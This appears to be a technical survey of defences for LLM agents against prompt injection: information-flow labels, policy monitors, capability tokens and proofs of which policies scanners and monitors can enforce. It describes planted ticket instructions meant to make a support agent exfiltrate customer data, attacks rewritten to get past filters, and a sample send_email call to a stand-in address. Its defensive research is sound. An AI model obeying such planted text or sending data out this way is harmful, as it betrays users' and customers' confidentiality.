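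FIDES can't establish which parts of the context shaped a model's output, so it gives the output the combined labels of everything the model read. Once the customer list is in the context, every later email counts as containing it, so this method is no more precise than the history rule. The integrity label causes a worse problem. Costa and colleagues propose that an agent may take consequential actions only on the basis of trusted data. An ordinary agent that has read ticket 4812 has untrusted text in its context, so this policy would stop it from sending any email, even the legitimate reply.

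FIDES gets around this by keeping untrusted text away from the main model. It stores the ticket's text in a variable and shows the main model only the variable's name. A second model, which has no tools, reads the text and drafts a reply into another variable. The main model can then make a call such as:

```text
send_email(to="j.reed@example.com", body=#query_llm_0)
```

The policy can require the choice of tool and the recipient to come from trusted data, while allowing the message body to contain untrusted data. In this example, the address would have to come from a verified customer record. The planted instructions may spoil the draft, but they can't change the recipient or trigger a database query. If the main model needs a fact from the ticket to choose its next step, the second model can answer yes or no, or pick from a fixed list, which leaves the attacker very little room to write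 instructions.

The guarantee covers data that moves directly from one place to another. Costa and colleagues note that an observer might still learn something from the tools the agent calls and the order it calls them in.

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, takes a related approach. According to Shi, He and colleagues, it works out a task's steps and how data moves between them from the user's request, so that untrusted data can't change which steps run. This suits a request such as "email Alice the March invoice" better than one such as "deal with ticket 4812", because the ticket contains most of what the agent needs to plan the job.

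### What the tests found

Researchers have tested most of these systems on AgentDojo, a set of simulated workplaces in which agents do ordinary jobs while reading planted instructions. *AgentDojo* (2024) introduced it with 97 tasks and 629 security tests. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts over 900 pairings of a user's task with an attacker's goal. The agent works with office documents, a bank account, travel bookings or the Slack messaging service, and the attacker's text sits where outsiders' text would normally appear, such as the body of an email. Ordinary code then checks the simulated world for the attack's effects, such as a money transfer or a sent message. The two main scores are the share of attacks that succeed and the share of users' tasks that the agent completes.

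Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% for an agent using GPT-4o, and Shi, He and colleagues report that the agent completed about as many tasks as before. On a second benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Progent also helped models that already resisted most attacks, such as Claude Sonnet 4, where the rate fell from 6.8% to 0.5%.

FIDES stopped every attack that violated its policy. On GPT-4o, Costa and colleagues counted 152 genuine attack successes against an ordinary agent and none against FIDES. The policy check stopped these attacks, rather than the handling of variables. No attacks genuinely succeeded against an ordinary agent with the same check, while 21 did against FIDES without it. FIDES used variables to recover some of the work that the check would otherwise block.

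FIDES recovered only part of the task completion lost to the check. Averaged equally over the four workplaces, the ordinary agent completed 84% of its tasks without the check and 42% with it, while FIDES completed 50% with the check. Costa and colleagues' headline gain of 8% compares the last two figures. FIDES still completed about 34 percentage points fewer tasks than the unprotected agent. A stronger model reduced the loss in some cases. With OpenAI's o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, up from 41% with GPT-4o.

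The perfect security score also depended on good labels. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in AgentDojo used it. This gave them a clean baseline, but a retailer doesn't have a list of where attackers will write.

Later tests by other teams are a better guide to how well these systems resist attacks. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) used a language model to rewrite each attack several times, guided only by how often earlier versions had worked. Against an undefended agent running on GPT-4o-mini, the rewritten attacks succeeded 52.4% of the time. Against PIGuard, a filter that looks for instructions in incoming text, the standard attack never succeeded, but the rewritten attacks did 28.0% of the time. Against Progent, the rewritten attacks succeeded 7.7% of the time, no more often than the standard attack. This would be expected if the monitor compares recipients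 and tool names, since rephrasing an instruction doesn't change the call it asks for. Still, 7.7% is well above the 1.0% reported in Progent's own paper, which used a different model.

Ma and colleagues also retested CaMeL. They found that it was the most effective of ten defenses overall, but that it reduced task completion the most on four of the five models. Progent reduced task completion by at most seven percentage points.

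Their results are grouped by how much the user left open, which makes them directly relevant to the support agent. On undefended GPT-4o-mini, the standard attack succeeded 43.3% of the time when the user specified everything, 63.9% when the agent had to find details such as a recipient in outside content, and 87.5% when outside content determined the action itself. "Deal with ticket 4812" belongs in that last group. Progent held the attack success rate to 11% or less in each group, but partly because its policies for many open-ended tasks allowed only tools that read data. The support agent couldn't answer customers under such a policy.

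AgentDojo's original attacks have become too easy for newer models to resist. In Ma and colleagues' tests, the standard attack succeeded only 0.3% of the time on Claude Haiku 4.5 with no defense. *The Devil is in the Context* (2026) reports that no attacks succeeded against any setup on a selection of the original cases. On newly written cases, attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time without a defense and 2.5% with CaMeL, which completed only 27.5% of tasks. PromptArmor, which has a language model clean incoming text, allowed 7.5% of attacks and completed 90% of tasks. All these attack rates are multiples of 2.5%, which suggests about 40 cases, so the security gap between CaMeL and PromptArmor may be only two attacks. The gap in completed tasks is much too large to be explained by the small number of cases.

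### Who writes the policy

All these results depend on somebody writing a good policy. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) argues that Progent's guarantees require correct and complete rules, and that people make mistakes when they write rules by hand. A good policy is even harder to write for a general-purpose assistant, because its next task may need permissions that nobody anticipated.

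Progent's answer is to have a language model write the policy. The model drafts the first version from the user's request, before the agent has read anything untrusted, and may propose changes as tool results come in. A solver then compares the calls that the old and new policies would allow. If *A*(*P*) is the set of calls that policy *P* allows, a new policy *P′* takes effect automatically only when

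```text
A(P′) ⊆ A(P)
```

A new policy needs approval if it would allow any call that the old one refused. Planted text might fool the model into proposing a new permission for `send_email`, but that change would need approval before taking effect. *Extending the Formalism* warns that malicious tool results could loosen Progent's policy during an update, and this check is meant to prevent that from happening unnoticed.

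Shi, He and colleagues compared several ways of running the system on AgentDojo, all with GPT-4o:

| Policy | Attack success |
|---|---|
| None | 39.9% |
| A model writes it once | 2.5% |
| A model writes and updates it, with every expansion approved automatically | 1.0% |
| A person reviews the first policy and every expansion | 0% |

Progent's headline figure of 1.0% comes from the third row, where the approver approves everything. The solver's warnings had no effect in that test, so the figure measures how well the model writes policies. Human review did better, and only 6% of updates needed it.

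That 6% could be misleading for the support agent. The worker's request to deal with ticket 4812 justifies little more than a call to `read_ticket`, so the model would propose almost every other permission after reading the stranger's text. A worker who approves such requests all day may stop reading them. But a support agent does much the same job on every ticket, which makes writing policies by hand much more practical than it is for a general assistant. The retailer can write fixed rules once, and Progent doesn't let a model-written policy allow anything those rules forbid.

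AgentSpec's tests also allow a comparison between people and a model, in this case o1:

| | Rules written by hand | Rules written by o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Risky programs caught | Over 90% | 87% |
| Hazardous household-robot tasks stopped | All | 71% |
| Driving scenarios without a violation | 8 of 8 | 5 of 8 |

People wrote better rules than o1 in each domain, most clearly for robots and cars. The comparison somewhat favours people, because they wrote their rules from the benchmarks' own descriptions of the risks. The model had worked examples for code and robots but none for driving. Since o1 is an old model, the gap may well have narrowed.

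A company can test a policy on live traffic before enforcing it. AWS offers a mode that logs what the monitor would have decided without refusing anything. Developers can use the log to find rules that are too strict, because it shows the ordinary work those rules would have blocked. Rules that are too loose are hard to find this way, because the log won't show a wrongly allowed call unless somebody attacks during the trial. Developers can look for those by analysing the policy itself before deployment, as AgentCap does.

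### When refusals cost work, and when they save it

Even a correct policy can stop an agent from completing its task. Sigdel and Baral replayed recorded sequences of tool calls under five sets of rules, from none to very strict, with dangerous calls and technical faults mixed in. The strictest set blocked 68% of the dangerous calls, but the share of tasks completed fell from 36% to 7%. The drop would probably be smaller for real agents, because the experiment used no language model. An agent can often read the reason for a refusal and try something else, which a replayed script can't do.

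Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026), in *Reason Less, Verify More*, found that refusals raised the number of completed tasks in one case. They used the airline part of τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service. Its tools don't enforce the airline's rules. For instance, the tool for cancelling a booking may cancel a non-refundable ticket without returning an error, so the agent doesn't notice that the database is now wrong. In their tests, 78% of the failures of an agent based on GPT-4o-mini were silent in this way.

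The three researchers added four small checks, which they call gates, that contain no language model. Before a tool changes anything, a gate reads the proposed call and the current database, then allows the call or refuses it with a reason. One gate checks whether a booking is eligible for cancellation, and the others cover baggage, passenger numbers, and changes to records that the agent hasn't read.

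Over 50 tasks with five attempts each, the success rate rose from 29.6% to 42.0%. A repeat with 15 new attempts per task showed almost the same gain, from 30.8% to 43.1%. The agent also became more consistent, completing 26% of tasks on all five attempts, up from 8%. Most of the improvement came from the 26 tasks where a gate blocked at least one call. Success on those tasks rose from 13.8% to 33.1%, while the change on the other tasks could be due to chance. With the stronger GPT-5.2, success rose from 61.2% to 71.6%, but Reddy and colleagues didn't repeat that test, and its margin of error ranges from almost no gain to a gain of about 21 points.

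One task shows why a gate outside the model can help. A simulated customer gives false information to get a cancellation that the rules forbid. Without the gate, agents handled this correctly at most once in 16 attempts. With it, they succeeded in all 16, because the gate uses the booking record, not the customer's claims.

Some gates were much more useful than others. The cancellation gate refused 161 calls, all correctly, and accounted for nearly all of the gain. The baggage gate refused 42 calls, only two of them correctly. When the researchers removed gates one at a time from a set of five candidates, removing the cancellation gate lowered the success rate, and removing any of the others raised it. Agents also don't always recover from a refusal. On one task, the agent kept getting the same refusal and failed all five attempts.

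The study has other limits. The gain comes from a single domain, and the researchers tested the gates on tasks they already had when they chose the gates. Some of the improvement may come from the explanations that accompany refusals, which hint at what the model should do next. The gates also let a call through if their own code crashes. That is reasonable for catching honest mistakes, but a monitor meant to stop attackers should refuse the call.

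Reddy and colleagues also tried gates on a simulated shop whose tools already enforce most of the relevant rules. The success rate fell from 62.5% to 57.8%, but the drop could be due to chance, and a bug in the gates explained much of it. They recommend leaving out the gate in such cases or building the rule into the tool. The retailer could do this by having `send_email` take a ticket number and look up the customer's address, so the model no longer supplies a recipient.

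## The case for one policy analysed beforehand and enforced afterwards

Some researchers want a check before deployment and another at run time, because each can establish things that the other can't. The survey *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026) describes the trade-off. An advance analysis can cover every run of a fixed workflow, but an agent's model generates much of its plan during the run. A monitor can handle whatever the model proposes, but when it approves a call it can't take later calls into account. The proposed solution is to write a single policy for the agent, analyse it for mistakes before deployment, and then enforce it on every call.

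A policy analyser checks the rules for any that allow too much or contradict each other, whereas a scanner checks the tools' code.

### A token for each call

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AgentCap*, apply Hardy's remedy for the confused deputy to agents. An AgentCap agent has no standing permission to use its tools. It has to obtain a token, which they call a capability, for each action. The retailer's policy might include these rules, adapted from their rule for bank payments:

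```text
grant send_email {
    action: write
    resource: "mail/outgoing"
    intent: [reply_to_customer]
    trust: >= 0.8
    requires: [read_ticket]
    ttl: 30s
    budget: 1
    deny_groups: [outgoing_mail]
    bound_params: [to]
}

deny_combination no_bulk_mail { customer_list + outgoing_mail }
```

When the model proposes an email, it also declares a purpose. AgentCap's policy engine then makes seven checks. It confirms that it hasn't locked the agent out, that the policy lists the tool, that the purpose is allowed, and that the agent's trust score is high enough. It checks that the agent already holds a valid token for `read_ticket` in this session, and that a token for `send_email` wouldn't complete a forbidden combination. It also checks where the value of `to` came from.

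The check on `to` provides most of the protection against ticket 4812. The retailer marks some sources as trusted, such as the worker's request and the address in a verified customer record, and others as untrusted, such as the text of tickets. The engine refuses a protected argument that only untrusted sources support, so it would refuse an outside address that appears only in the stranger's text. The purpose check wouldn't catch that address, because the model supplies the purpose, and a hijacked model can falsely give it as replying to a customer.

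If the request passes all seven checks, the engine issues a signed token that is valid for one call within 30 seconds. A separate gateway in front of the tool verifies the signature, the time limit and the remaining budget, and confirms that the token was issued to this agent for this action. It forwards the call only if all of these checks pass. Issuing and verifying a token together typically take about 0.15 milliseconds.

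The trust score could be a nuisance because it falls quickly and recovers slowly. By default it starts at 0.8, and each refusal or suspicious result multiplies it by 0.7. Three in a row bring it to 0.27, and AgentCap locks an agent out below 0.3. A normal result closes only 1% of the gap between the score and 1. With the 0.8 requirement above, which comes from the published bank rule, one refusal would stop the agent from sending email until it had produced 79 normal results. If the model made one honest mistake on a ticket, the agent probably couldn't answer it.

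### A permission that nobody could use

Before deployment, AgentCap's analyser checks every pair of permissions to see whether an agent could hold both at once. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao ran it on a customer-service policy with eight permissions, which make 28 pairs. The policy forbids six of these pairs, and none of the other 22 combines access to sensitive data with a way to send it out.

The analyser also found that no agent could ever use `delete_customer`, because a prerequisite conflicted with an exclusion. The simplest conflict of this kind looks like this, where `P` is some other permission:

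```text
delete_customer requires P
delete_customer may not be held together with P
```

Each rule could look sensible to the person who wrote it. At run time the monitor would refuse every deletion, and every refusal would be correct under the policy, so staff might blame the model. The researchers corrected a similar conflict in a banking policy with 11 permissions. The analyser then confirmed that an agent could obtain the permissions for all six jobs the policy describes.

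Suppose the retailer runs the same analysis while `query_orders` still accepts any SQL, and puts that tool in the `customer_list` group. The analyser would report that no agent can handle a ticket, since the job needs both `query_orders` and `send_email`. If the retailer removed the ban, the analyser would report a possible leak instead. Changing the rules alone would not solve this, so the retailer would have to give the agent the repaired `query_orders`, which takes a customer number, and keep the ban for a separate tool that reads the whole list.

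Because AgentCap works in pairs, it converts a ban on a combination of three groups into a broader ban on each pair. Willison's lethal trifecta is dangerous when all three elements are present, but an AgentCap ban on it would stop the support agent from sending any reply after reading a ticket.

### What AgentCap stopped

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested the monitor on two benchmarks of planted instructions, AgentDojo (949 attacked cases and 97 ordinary tasks) and InjecAgent (1,054 attacked cases).

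| | AgentDojo, GPT-4o | AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | InjecAgent, GPT-4o | InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attack success without AgentCap | 45.63% | 33.23% | 23.24% | 11.95% |
| Attack success with AgentCap | 5.09% | 0% | 8.63% | 0% |
| Drop in tasks completed without attack | 3.1 points | 7.2 points | 11.7 points | 5.9 points |

On AgentDojo, the drops of 3.1 and 7.2 points amount to three and seven tasks. The researchers ran each test once, so the difference between the two models may well be chance. The attacks were also fixed in advance. Ma and colleagues rewrote attacks to suit other defenses, but nobody did this for AgentCap, so the zeros don't show how it would do against an attacker who studied the policy.

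AgentCap did better than Progent, the monitor whose policies a model can write, on security and completed tasks. With GPT-4o, agents under AgentCap completed 78% of tasks without an attack and 75% during one, compared with 68% and 60% under Progent. But Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote AgentCap's policies themselves, from the benchmark's descriptions of its tools and users' tasks, and froze them before testing. GPT-4o wrote Progent's policies during each task, and often limited arguments to values it had anticipated, which blocked legitimate calls. Some of AgentCap's lead therefore probably comes from having human policy writers who knew the tasks.

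Three kinds of attack still succeeded on GPT-4o. Some targeted only the agent's written answer, and no check on tool calls can stop those. Others put the attacker's value in an argument that the policy didn't protect, such as the body of an email. In the rest, the policy protected the argument, but the attacker's value came from a field that nobody had marked as untrusted. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao call the last two kinds gaps in the policy, and suggest extending the analyser to flag them. But finding an unmarked field requires knowing which fields outsiders can write to. The rules don't contain that information, but a scanner that traces data from its sources might supply it.

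### When a wider permission breaks a job

Companies also edit their policies. *Agenra* (Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) shows that when permissions get used up, loosening a rule can stop an agent from doing work it could do before.

Suppose the support agent may send one email to the courier and one to the customer, and the monitor counts each email against the first permission on the list that fits. A manager then widens the first permission to cover either recipient.

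| Permissions, in order | Email customer, then courier | Email customer twice |
|---|---|---|
| Courier once; customer once | Allowed | Second email refused |
| Courier or customer once; customer once | Second email refused | Allowed |

After the change, the email to the customer uses up the first permission, and the second doesn't allow the agent to email the courier. The agent can no longer finish the job, but it can now email the customer twice, which the old policy prevented. A test that emailed the courier first would pass under both policies.

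Agenra checks such edits before they take effect by looking for a proof that the new list will accept every call the old list would have accepted, however many calls came before. The researchers wrote 51 test edits, 21 of which kept every old job working. Agenra certified all 21 and none of the other 30. It also certified a real change by the developers of Dyad, an open-source app builder, who raised a limit on free messages from five to ten. Checking an edit took about a tenth of a second. Exploring every possible sequence of calls is much slower. For an agent with six tools, searching sequences of up to six events took under a second, but searching those of up to eight took more than two and a half minutes.

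Certification means only that tasks that worked before an edit still work, so safety needs a separate check. Agenra also certified an edit that let an agent send the public summary of a confidential report twice instead of once, because the edit didn't break any existing task.

The same policy governs the agent at run time. The researchers wrote the core of the monitor in Lean, a language in which a computer can check proofs about programs. One proof shows that if the policy requires an argument to come from a particular tool, every call the core accepts meets that requirement. The proofs don't cover the Python code that translates the policy and runs the tools.

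They also cannot supply a rule that nobody wrote. In trials with live agents, fixed attacks led an unguarded Qwen model to send the confidential report in 15 of 20 runs. Agenra and a simple guard that the researchers wrote by hand each reduced this to none. But Agenra's policy then lacked a rule about where a message's text must come from, and when the researchers replayed the agents' calls, Agenra accepted five calls that the hand-written guard refused. The researchers have since added the rule. *Tether* (2026) presents a related system that can prove a policy keeps chosen properties over call sequences of any length, though a person still has to choose the properties.

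### Permissions that combine across agents

When a company runs several agents, one can also influence another through text, as in AgentFlow's example of the research and operations agents. AgentCap doesn't stop this. It lets a supervising agent pass part of its authority to a worker agent, and the worker's token can't outlast the supervisor's or allow more calls.

Suppose the retailer's complaints agent writes case summaries and can pay a refund once it has approval. A second agent reads the summaries and approves refunds. Each has only the permissions it needs. But if a stranger hijacks the complaints agent, it can write a summary that gets its own refund approved.

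Parisel (2026), in *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI*, proposes a way to find such arrangements at the design stage. The method draws a graph of the company's agents. An arrow can run from one agent to another if the first can write to something the second reads, or if the two can exchange messages. Parisel keeps the arrow only if the resources involved are far enough apart in the company's structure, according to this distance:

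```text
d(a, b) = F × 2^−(2D + 1)
```

Here *D* is the depth in the company's hierarchy of the smallest unit that contains both resources, and *F* rises from 1 to 2 with their sensitivity. In Parisel's worked example, the smallest unit that contains both a finance report and an engineering deployment policy is a division at depth 1, and *F* is 1.75. Their distance is 1.75 × 2⁻³, or about 0.22, exactly the threshold Parisel sets for keeping an arrow.

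The analysis then searches the graph for three patterns. In the first, an agent can influence another whose approval it needs, like the complaints agent. In the second, an agent that grants access can influence the agent that receives it. The third is a chain of influence between areas the company wants to keep apart. The method also limits each agent's reach, which includes the permissions of every agent it can influence, and requires explicit approval for each arrow.

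The threshold can hide problems between agents whose resources are close together. If both of the retailer's agents work within one small department at depth 3, the distance between their resources is at most 2 × 2⁻⁷, or about 0.016. The graph would have no arrow between the agents at Parisel's threshold, so the analysis would miss the refund problem. The retailer could lower the threshold, but it would then have more arrows to review. Parisel illustrates the method on ten invented agents and doesn't measure how many real problems it finds or how many false alarms it raises. The method is best used to decide where to put an approval step or a runtime check, as Parisel recommends.

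### Proving some rules and monitoring the rest

In all these systems, the monitor still checks every call after the analysis. An older idea is for the analysis to remove some of the checks. Bodden, Lam and Hendren developed it for Java programs in *Partially evaluating finite-state runtime monitors ahead of time*. Their running example is a rule that a program must not write to a network connection after closing it. An ordinary monitor watches every command that closes, reopens or writes to a connection, which can severely slow the program.

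Their tool, Clara, first tries to prove that some of those commands can't lead to a violation. If the program never writes to any connection, it can't break the rule, and Clara removes the monitor. Otherwise Clara analyses each connection separately, because closing one and writing to another is harmless. It then checks the order of commands, since a write that always comes before the close is harmless too. The remaining checks form a residual monitor, which catches exactly the violations the full monitor would have caught.

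In 68% of test cases, Clara proved that the program could never break the rule, so no monitor was necessary. It proved only once that a program would definitely break a rule. Bodden, Lam and Hendren explain in *Clara* that no tool can always find the smallest possible residual monitor, because it would have to predict the program's future behaviour and inputs. *Control-Flow Residual Analysis for Symbolic Automata* (2017) extends the approach and, in its case study, cuts the average slowdown from 97% to as little as 4%.

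The retailer could do something similar if it used the version of `send_email` that looks up the address itself. An analysis of the code might then prove that every email goes to the ticket's customer, whatever the model does, and the monitor could stop checking recipients. The original tool takes the address from the model, so the analysis can't prove this and the monitor still has to check.

Agents probably gain less from this than Java programs do. A Java program's code largely determines the order of its operations, whereas an agent's model chooses the order as it works, so the analysis can prove less beforehand. Skipping run-time checks would also save less time, since AgentCap's checks take a fraction of a millisecond and a model's reply usually takes seconds. The main benefit would be a shorter policy, with fewer rules for people to get wrong.

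*Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) deals with the lack of a fixed order by having the model write a plan in a small programming language before the agent calls any tool. A theorem prover checks whether every path through the plan obeys the policy. If the check fails, the model gets up to eight more tries. A monitor then checks each call, because the agent may depart from its plan and some plans never pass.

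Their tests on 50 airline tasks from τ²-bench show why they kept the monitor. Without either check, an agent using GPT-5.4-mini broke the policy 13 times. Verifying its plans reduced violations only to 10, and supplying ready-made parts for the plans left them at 12. Adding the monitor eliminated violations and raised the share of tasks completed without one from 50% to 60%.

The finding of zero violations is nearly true by definition, because the researchers counted violations of the same rules that the monitor enforces. They also didn't test the monitor without the verified plans, so the results don't show how much the plans contribute. The best of the other systems they tried, a monitor running AgentSpec rules, reached 50%. Soteria's plans may account for some of the difference, but Soteria cost about four times as much per task.

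### Whether a tool does what its label says

All these analyses rely on descriptions of tools. If the retailer's policy labels `read_ticket` as a tool that only reads, but the function also sends a copy of each ticket to an outside analytics company, AgentCap's analyser will find no leak and the monitor will allow every call. The researchers acknowledge this dependence. Soteria's proofs assume that tools behave as described, and Agenra's assume that a tool has only the effects its developer declared. In one of Agenra's tests, the monitor failed to stop a tool from making an undeclared deletion.

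Wrong tool descriptions are common. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, compared descriptions with code for 19,200 tools from 2,214 MCP servers. They used program analysis to collect the code behind each tool and a language model to judge whether it matched the description. The descriptions of 1,907 tools, or 9.9%, didn't match, and 35% of servers had at least one such tool. Another 2,170 tools had no description.

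Many of these mismatches wouldn't undermine a security policy. In the most common kind, 35% of the total, the description overstated what the tool could do. About a quarter, or some 470 tools, mainly involved side effects that the description left out, such as changing files or sending data elsewhere. These are the most likely to make a policy's labels wrong.

The true number of mismatches is probably higher. When the researchers checked 200 tools that their system had passed, they found five mismatches. At that rate, the system would have missed about 380 mismatches among the 15,123 tools it passed. Including those would bring the total to around 13% of the tools with descriptions. This estimate is rough because it rests on only five mismatches.

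A company therefore still has to examine its tools' code, and a general-purpose scanner won't be enough. Semgrep raised alerts for 5 of 197 confirmed mismatches, Bandit for 34, and Agent Scan, which is designed for MCP, for 50. These scanners look for dangerous code, but a function that uploads a ticket may be ordinary code with the wrong label. A system such as ACaM, which works out what each tool can do from its source code, is a more promising source of labels.

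A monitor can catch a mislabelled tool only if the error appears in the tool's output. Soteria compares each result with the tool's description and stops the run if they disagree. This would expose a weather tool that returned exchange rates, a mix-up that Shi, Zhang and colleagues found on a real server. It would miss one that returned the right forecast but also recorded who had asked for it.

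## What each method can establish in principle

Some limits on scanners and monitors have been proven mathematically, so better engineering can't remove them. In these proofs, an execution is the sequence of actions a program takes in one run, such as `read_ticket`, `query_orders`, `send_email`. The sequence is infinite if the program never stops. A security policy is a condition on a program's executions. Most policies apply to each execution separately, but some depend on how executions compare with one another.

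### Why no scanner is always right

Rice's theorem covers questions about what a program does, not what its text looks like. If some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no procedure can correctly sort every program into the two groups. *LLMs versus the Halting Problem* (2026) lists examples of such questions, including whether a program can ever reach a given state and whether two programs are equivalent. A scanner can always determine whether a file contains the text `send_email`, but it can't determine, for every program, whether the program will ever call `send_email` with a customer's record.

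The proof starts from the halting problem, the question of whether a given program eventually stops. Suppose a procedure could always answer it. A programmer could then write a program that runs the procedure on its own code, loops forever if the answer is "stops", and stops if the answer is "runs forever". Either answer would be wrong, so no such procedure exists.

Now take any program `M` and any input `w`, and write this:

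```python
def handle_ticket():
    simulate(M, w)   # runs M on w, without access to any tool
    send_email(to="drop@example.net", body=customer_record)
```

The function emails the record if and only if `M` halts on `w`. A scanner that could correctly predict whether the email is sent for every `M` and `w` would therefore solve the halting problem, which is impossible.

Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, applies the same construction to programs that an AI agent writes and a gatekeeper must approve. One example is a short, readable program that goes through the even numbers from 4 upwards and performs a forbidden action only if it finds one that isn't the sum of two primes. The program is safe exactly when Goldbach's conjecture is true, and nobody had proved it when Pérez-Acle wrote.

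If a program emails the record, anyone who runs it for long enough will see it happen, but running a program can't prove that it never will, however long it runs.

### Choosing which way to be wrong

A scanner that gives every program a yes or a no must be wrong about some of them, but its designers can choose which kind of error it makes. A sound scanner never clears a program that can break the policy. It uses over-approximation, which means treating any behavior it can't rule out as possible, so it also reports some harmless programs, such as `handle_ticket` when `M` never stops. An unsound scanner can raise fewer false alarms, but it will clear some dangerous programs.

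An analysis is sound only for the behaviour it covers. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) proves a soundness theorem about skills, which are packages of instructions and code for agents. The theorem covers a skill's code, settings and metadata, but not the model's outputs or any commands the skill assembles while it runs.

A company can often tolerate a sound scanner's false alarms because, as Pérez-Acle shows, it needs only a checkable list that includes every program it must accept and none that it must refuse, rather than a correct verdict on every program. The retailer could accept only agents whose `send_email` looks up the customer's address itself, and reject all others without further analysis. This would mean rejecting some safe agents. Pérez-Acle measured how often this happens across every possible program of a very simple kind, using a rule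 that accepted only programs with no forbidden action anywhere in them. The rule accepted 71.9% of the safe programs with three states, but only 47.3% of those with five.

A time limit makes the question answerable, since a checker can run the program until the limit and observe what it does. But Pérez-Acle proves that a checker that is always right must take roughly that long on some programs. The proof again uses a program that runs the checker on itself and does the opposite of what the checker predicts, so any early verdict is wrong. A scanner that is always faster than running the program must therefore sometimes give a wrong answer or no answer.

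### When the unknown part is a model

The main difficulty in scanning the support agent is that nobody can list what the model will write. The halting problem matters less because the agent's loop is simple. *PACE* (2026) points out that a tool description's effect on behaviour depends on the whole context, including any injected text, and that no audit can cover every context. There are also too many possible outputs to check one by one. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, a 100-token reply can take 10⁵⁰⁰ forms, and a conservative scanner has to treat all of them as possible.

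Under that assumption, it is easy to show that the original support agent can email a customer's record to a stranger, because some string of text requests exactly that. The same is true of almost any agent that can read records and choose whom to email, however well its model resists attacks. The scanner correctly finds that the code allows this, but that finding doesn't help the retailer tell a risky model from a reliable one.

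A favourable result is much more useful, because it holds for any text a stranger writes and for any model the retailer later adopts.

### What a monitor can enforce by halting

A monitor avoids the halting problem because it acts while the program runs. It can block the email if `handle_ticket` reaches its last line, so there is no need to determine beforehand whether the program will get there.

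Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, worked out what this approach can achieve. He considered monitors that observe one execution, step by step, and can halt it. They have no information about future steps or about other executions. Schneider proved that such a monitor can enforce at most safety properties, which are policies whose violations always show in a finite prefix, meaning the first part of an execution. In symbols, with σ[1..i] for the first *i* actions of an execution σ:

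```text
if σ breaks the policy, then for some i
every execution that begins with σ[1..i] breaks the policy
```

"Never email a customer's record to an outsider" is a safety property because the agent can't undo the violation once it has sent the email. If a violation never showed in any prefix of the run (the actions taken up to some point), the monitor would have no basis for halting the agent.

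Schneider draws these policies as security automata, which are diagrams of states and the steps allowed from each. His example forbids sending messages after reading a file. The version for "no email after reading a customer record" looks like this:

```text
   any call but                       any call but
   query_orders                       send_email
     ┌────┐                             ┌────┐
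     │    ▼                             │    ▼
   ┌─────────┐      query_orders      ┌─────────┐
──►│ no_read │ ─────────────────────► │  read   │
   └─────────┘                        └─────────┘
```

The monitor starts in `no_read` and stays there when the agent calls `read_ticket`. A call to `query_orders` moves it to `read`. The `read` state has no transition for `send_email`, so the monitor halts the agent if it then tries to send an email.

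This policy would also block most legitimate replies, so only another customer's rows should trigger the middle arrow in the retailer's history rule. *Tether* can enforce a similar rule that blocks network access after an agent reads a sensitive file, with the same limits.

A monitor still can't enforce some safety properties. "Answer every ticket within 24 hours" is a safety property, because a violation is evident as soon as the time is up. But a monitor can't prevent the violation, because it can't stop time from passing, and halting the agent won't produce an answer.

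### Policies that no single execution can settle

Without the deadline, the rule becomes "every customer eventually gets an answer", which is a liveness property rather than a safety property. However long a customer has waited, the answer may still come, so no finite prefix shows a violation.

Other policies compare executions. Non-interference requires that secret information make no difference to what an outsider can observe. Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026), in *Local Allow, Global Deny*, give the example of a scheduling assistant that may reveal when its user is free but not why the user is busy. Consider two runs with the same request and the same free slots. In one, the user is busy on Tuesday with a team meeting, and the assistant offers Wednesday. In the other, the user has a confidential interview on Tuesday, and the assistant offers Thursday. Each offer is harmless in isolation,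 but together they show that the secret reason affected the choice. The policy requires, for every pair of runs:

```text
same request and same free slots  ⇒  same slots offered
```

Pandey and colleagues prove that a monitor that examines one run at a time and never raises a false alarm cannot detect any violation of this policy. Any single offer could have come from an assistant that ignores the reasons, so the monitor has to allow it. They also showed nine language models an example of such a violation. The models approved almost every action when they judged the actions one at a time, but flagged the violation when they saw both runs.

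A monitor can prevent these leaks by enforcing a stricter rule, such as blocking every offer once the assistant has read a private reason, but this also blocks harmless offers. FIDES, the system that attaches labels to data, makes a similar tradeoff.

Comparing runs is harder for agents than for ordinary programs because a model can give different answers to the same input. If two runs produce different offers, the difference may be due to chance rather than the secret. Pandey and colleagues show that a monitor would need many runs to distinguish the two causes, and even then would have only statistical evidence.

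### Scanning, monitoring and rewriting compared

*Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) puts scanners and monitors into one mathematical model and adds program rewriting, which changes a program before it runs. The rewritten program must obey the policy, and if the original already obeyed it, the two must behave equivalently.

| Method | Policies it can enforce exactly | Example |
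|---|---|---|
| Static analysis | Those for which a procedure can always answer yes or no | The program stops within 100 steps |
| Monitoring | Some of those for which a procedure can confirm every violation in finite time | The program never writes to the disk's boot sector |
| Rewriting | Nearly all of the above and some others, though not every policy | The program behaves as if a secret file did not exist |

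The middle row is marked "some" because a monitor must also be able to act in time. If a service has lent a program a resource and can't take it back, detecting misuse of that resource doesn't prevent it.

The secret-file policy is a case of non-interference, so no monitor can enforce it exactly. A rewriter can enforce it by removing the file's name from every directory listing the program receives. It doesn't need to determine whether the original program would have reacted to the name. The retailer does much the same by hand when it changes `query_orders` to return only the rows for the ticket's customer, so other customers' orders can no longer influence a reply through that tool.

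In this model, monitoring is strictly more powerful than static analysis because a monitor can run the static analysis when the program loads and then watch the execution. But Hamlen and colleagues assume that the monitor can read the program's code. They note that if a static analysis and a monitor receive different information, each may be able to enforce policies that the other can't.

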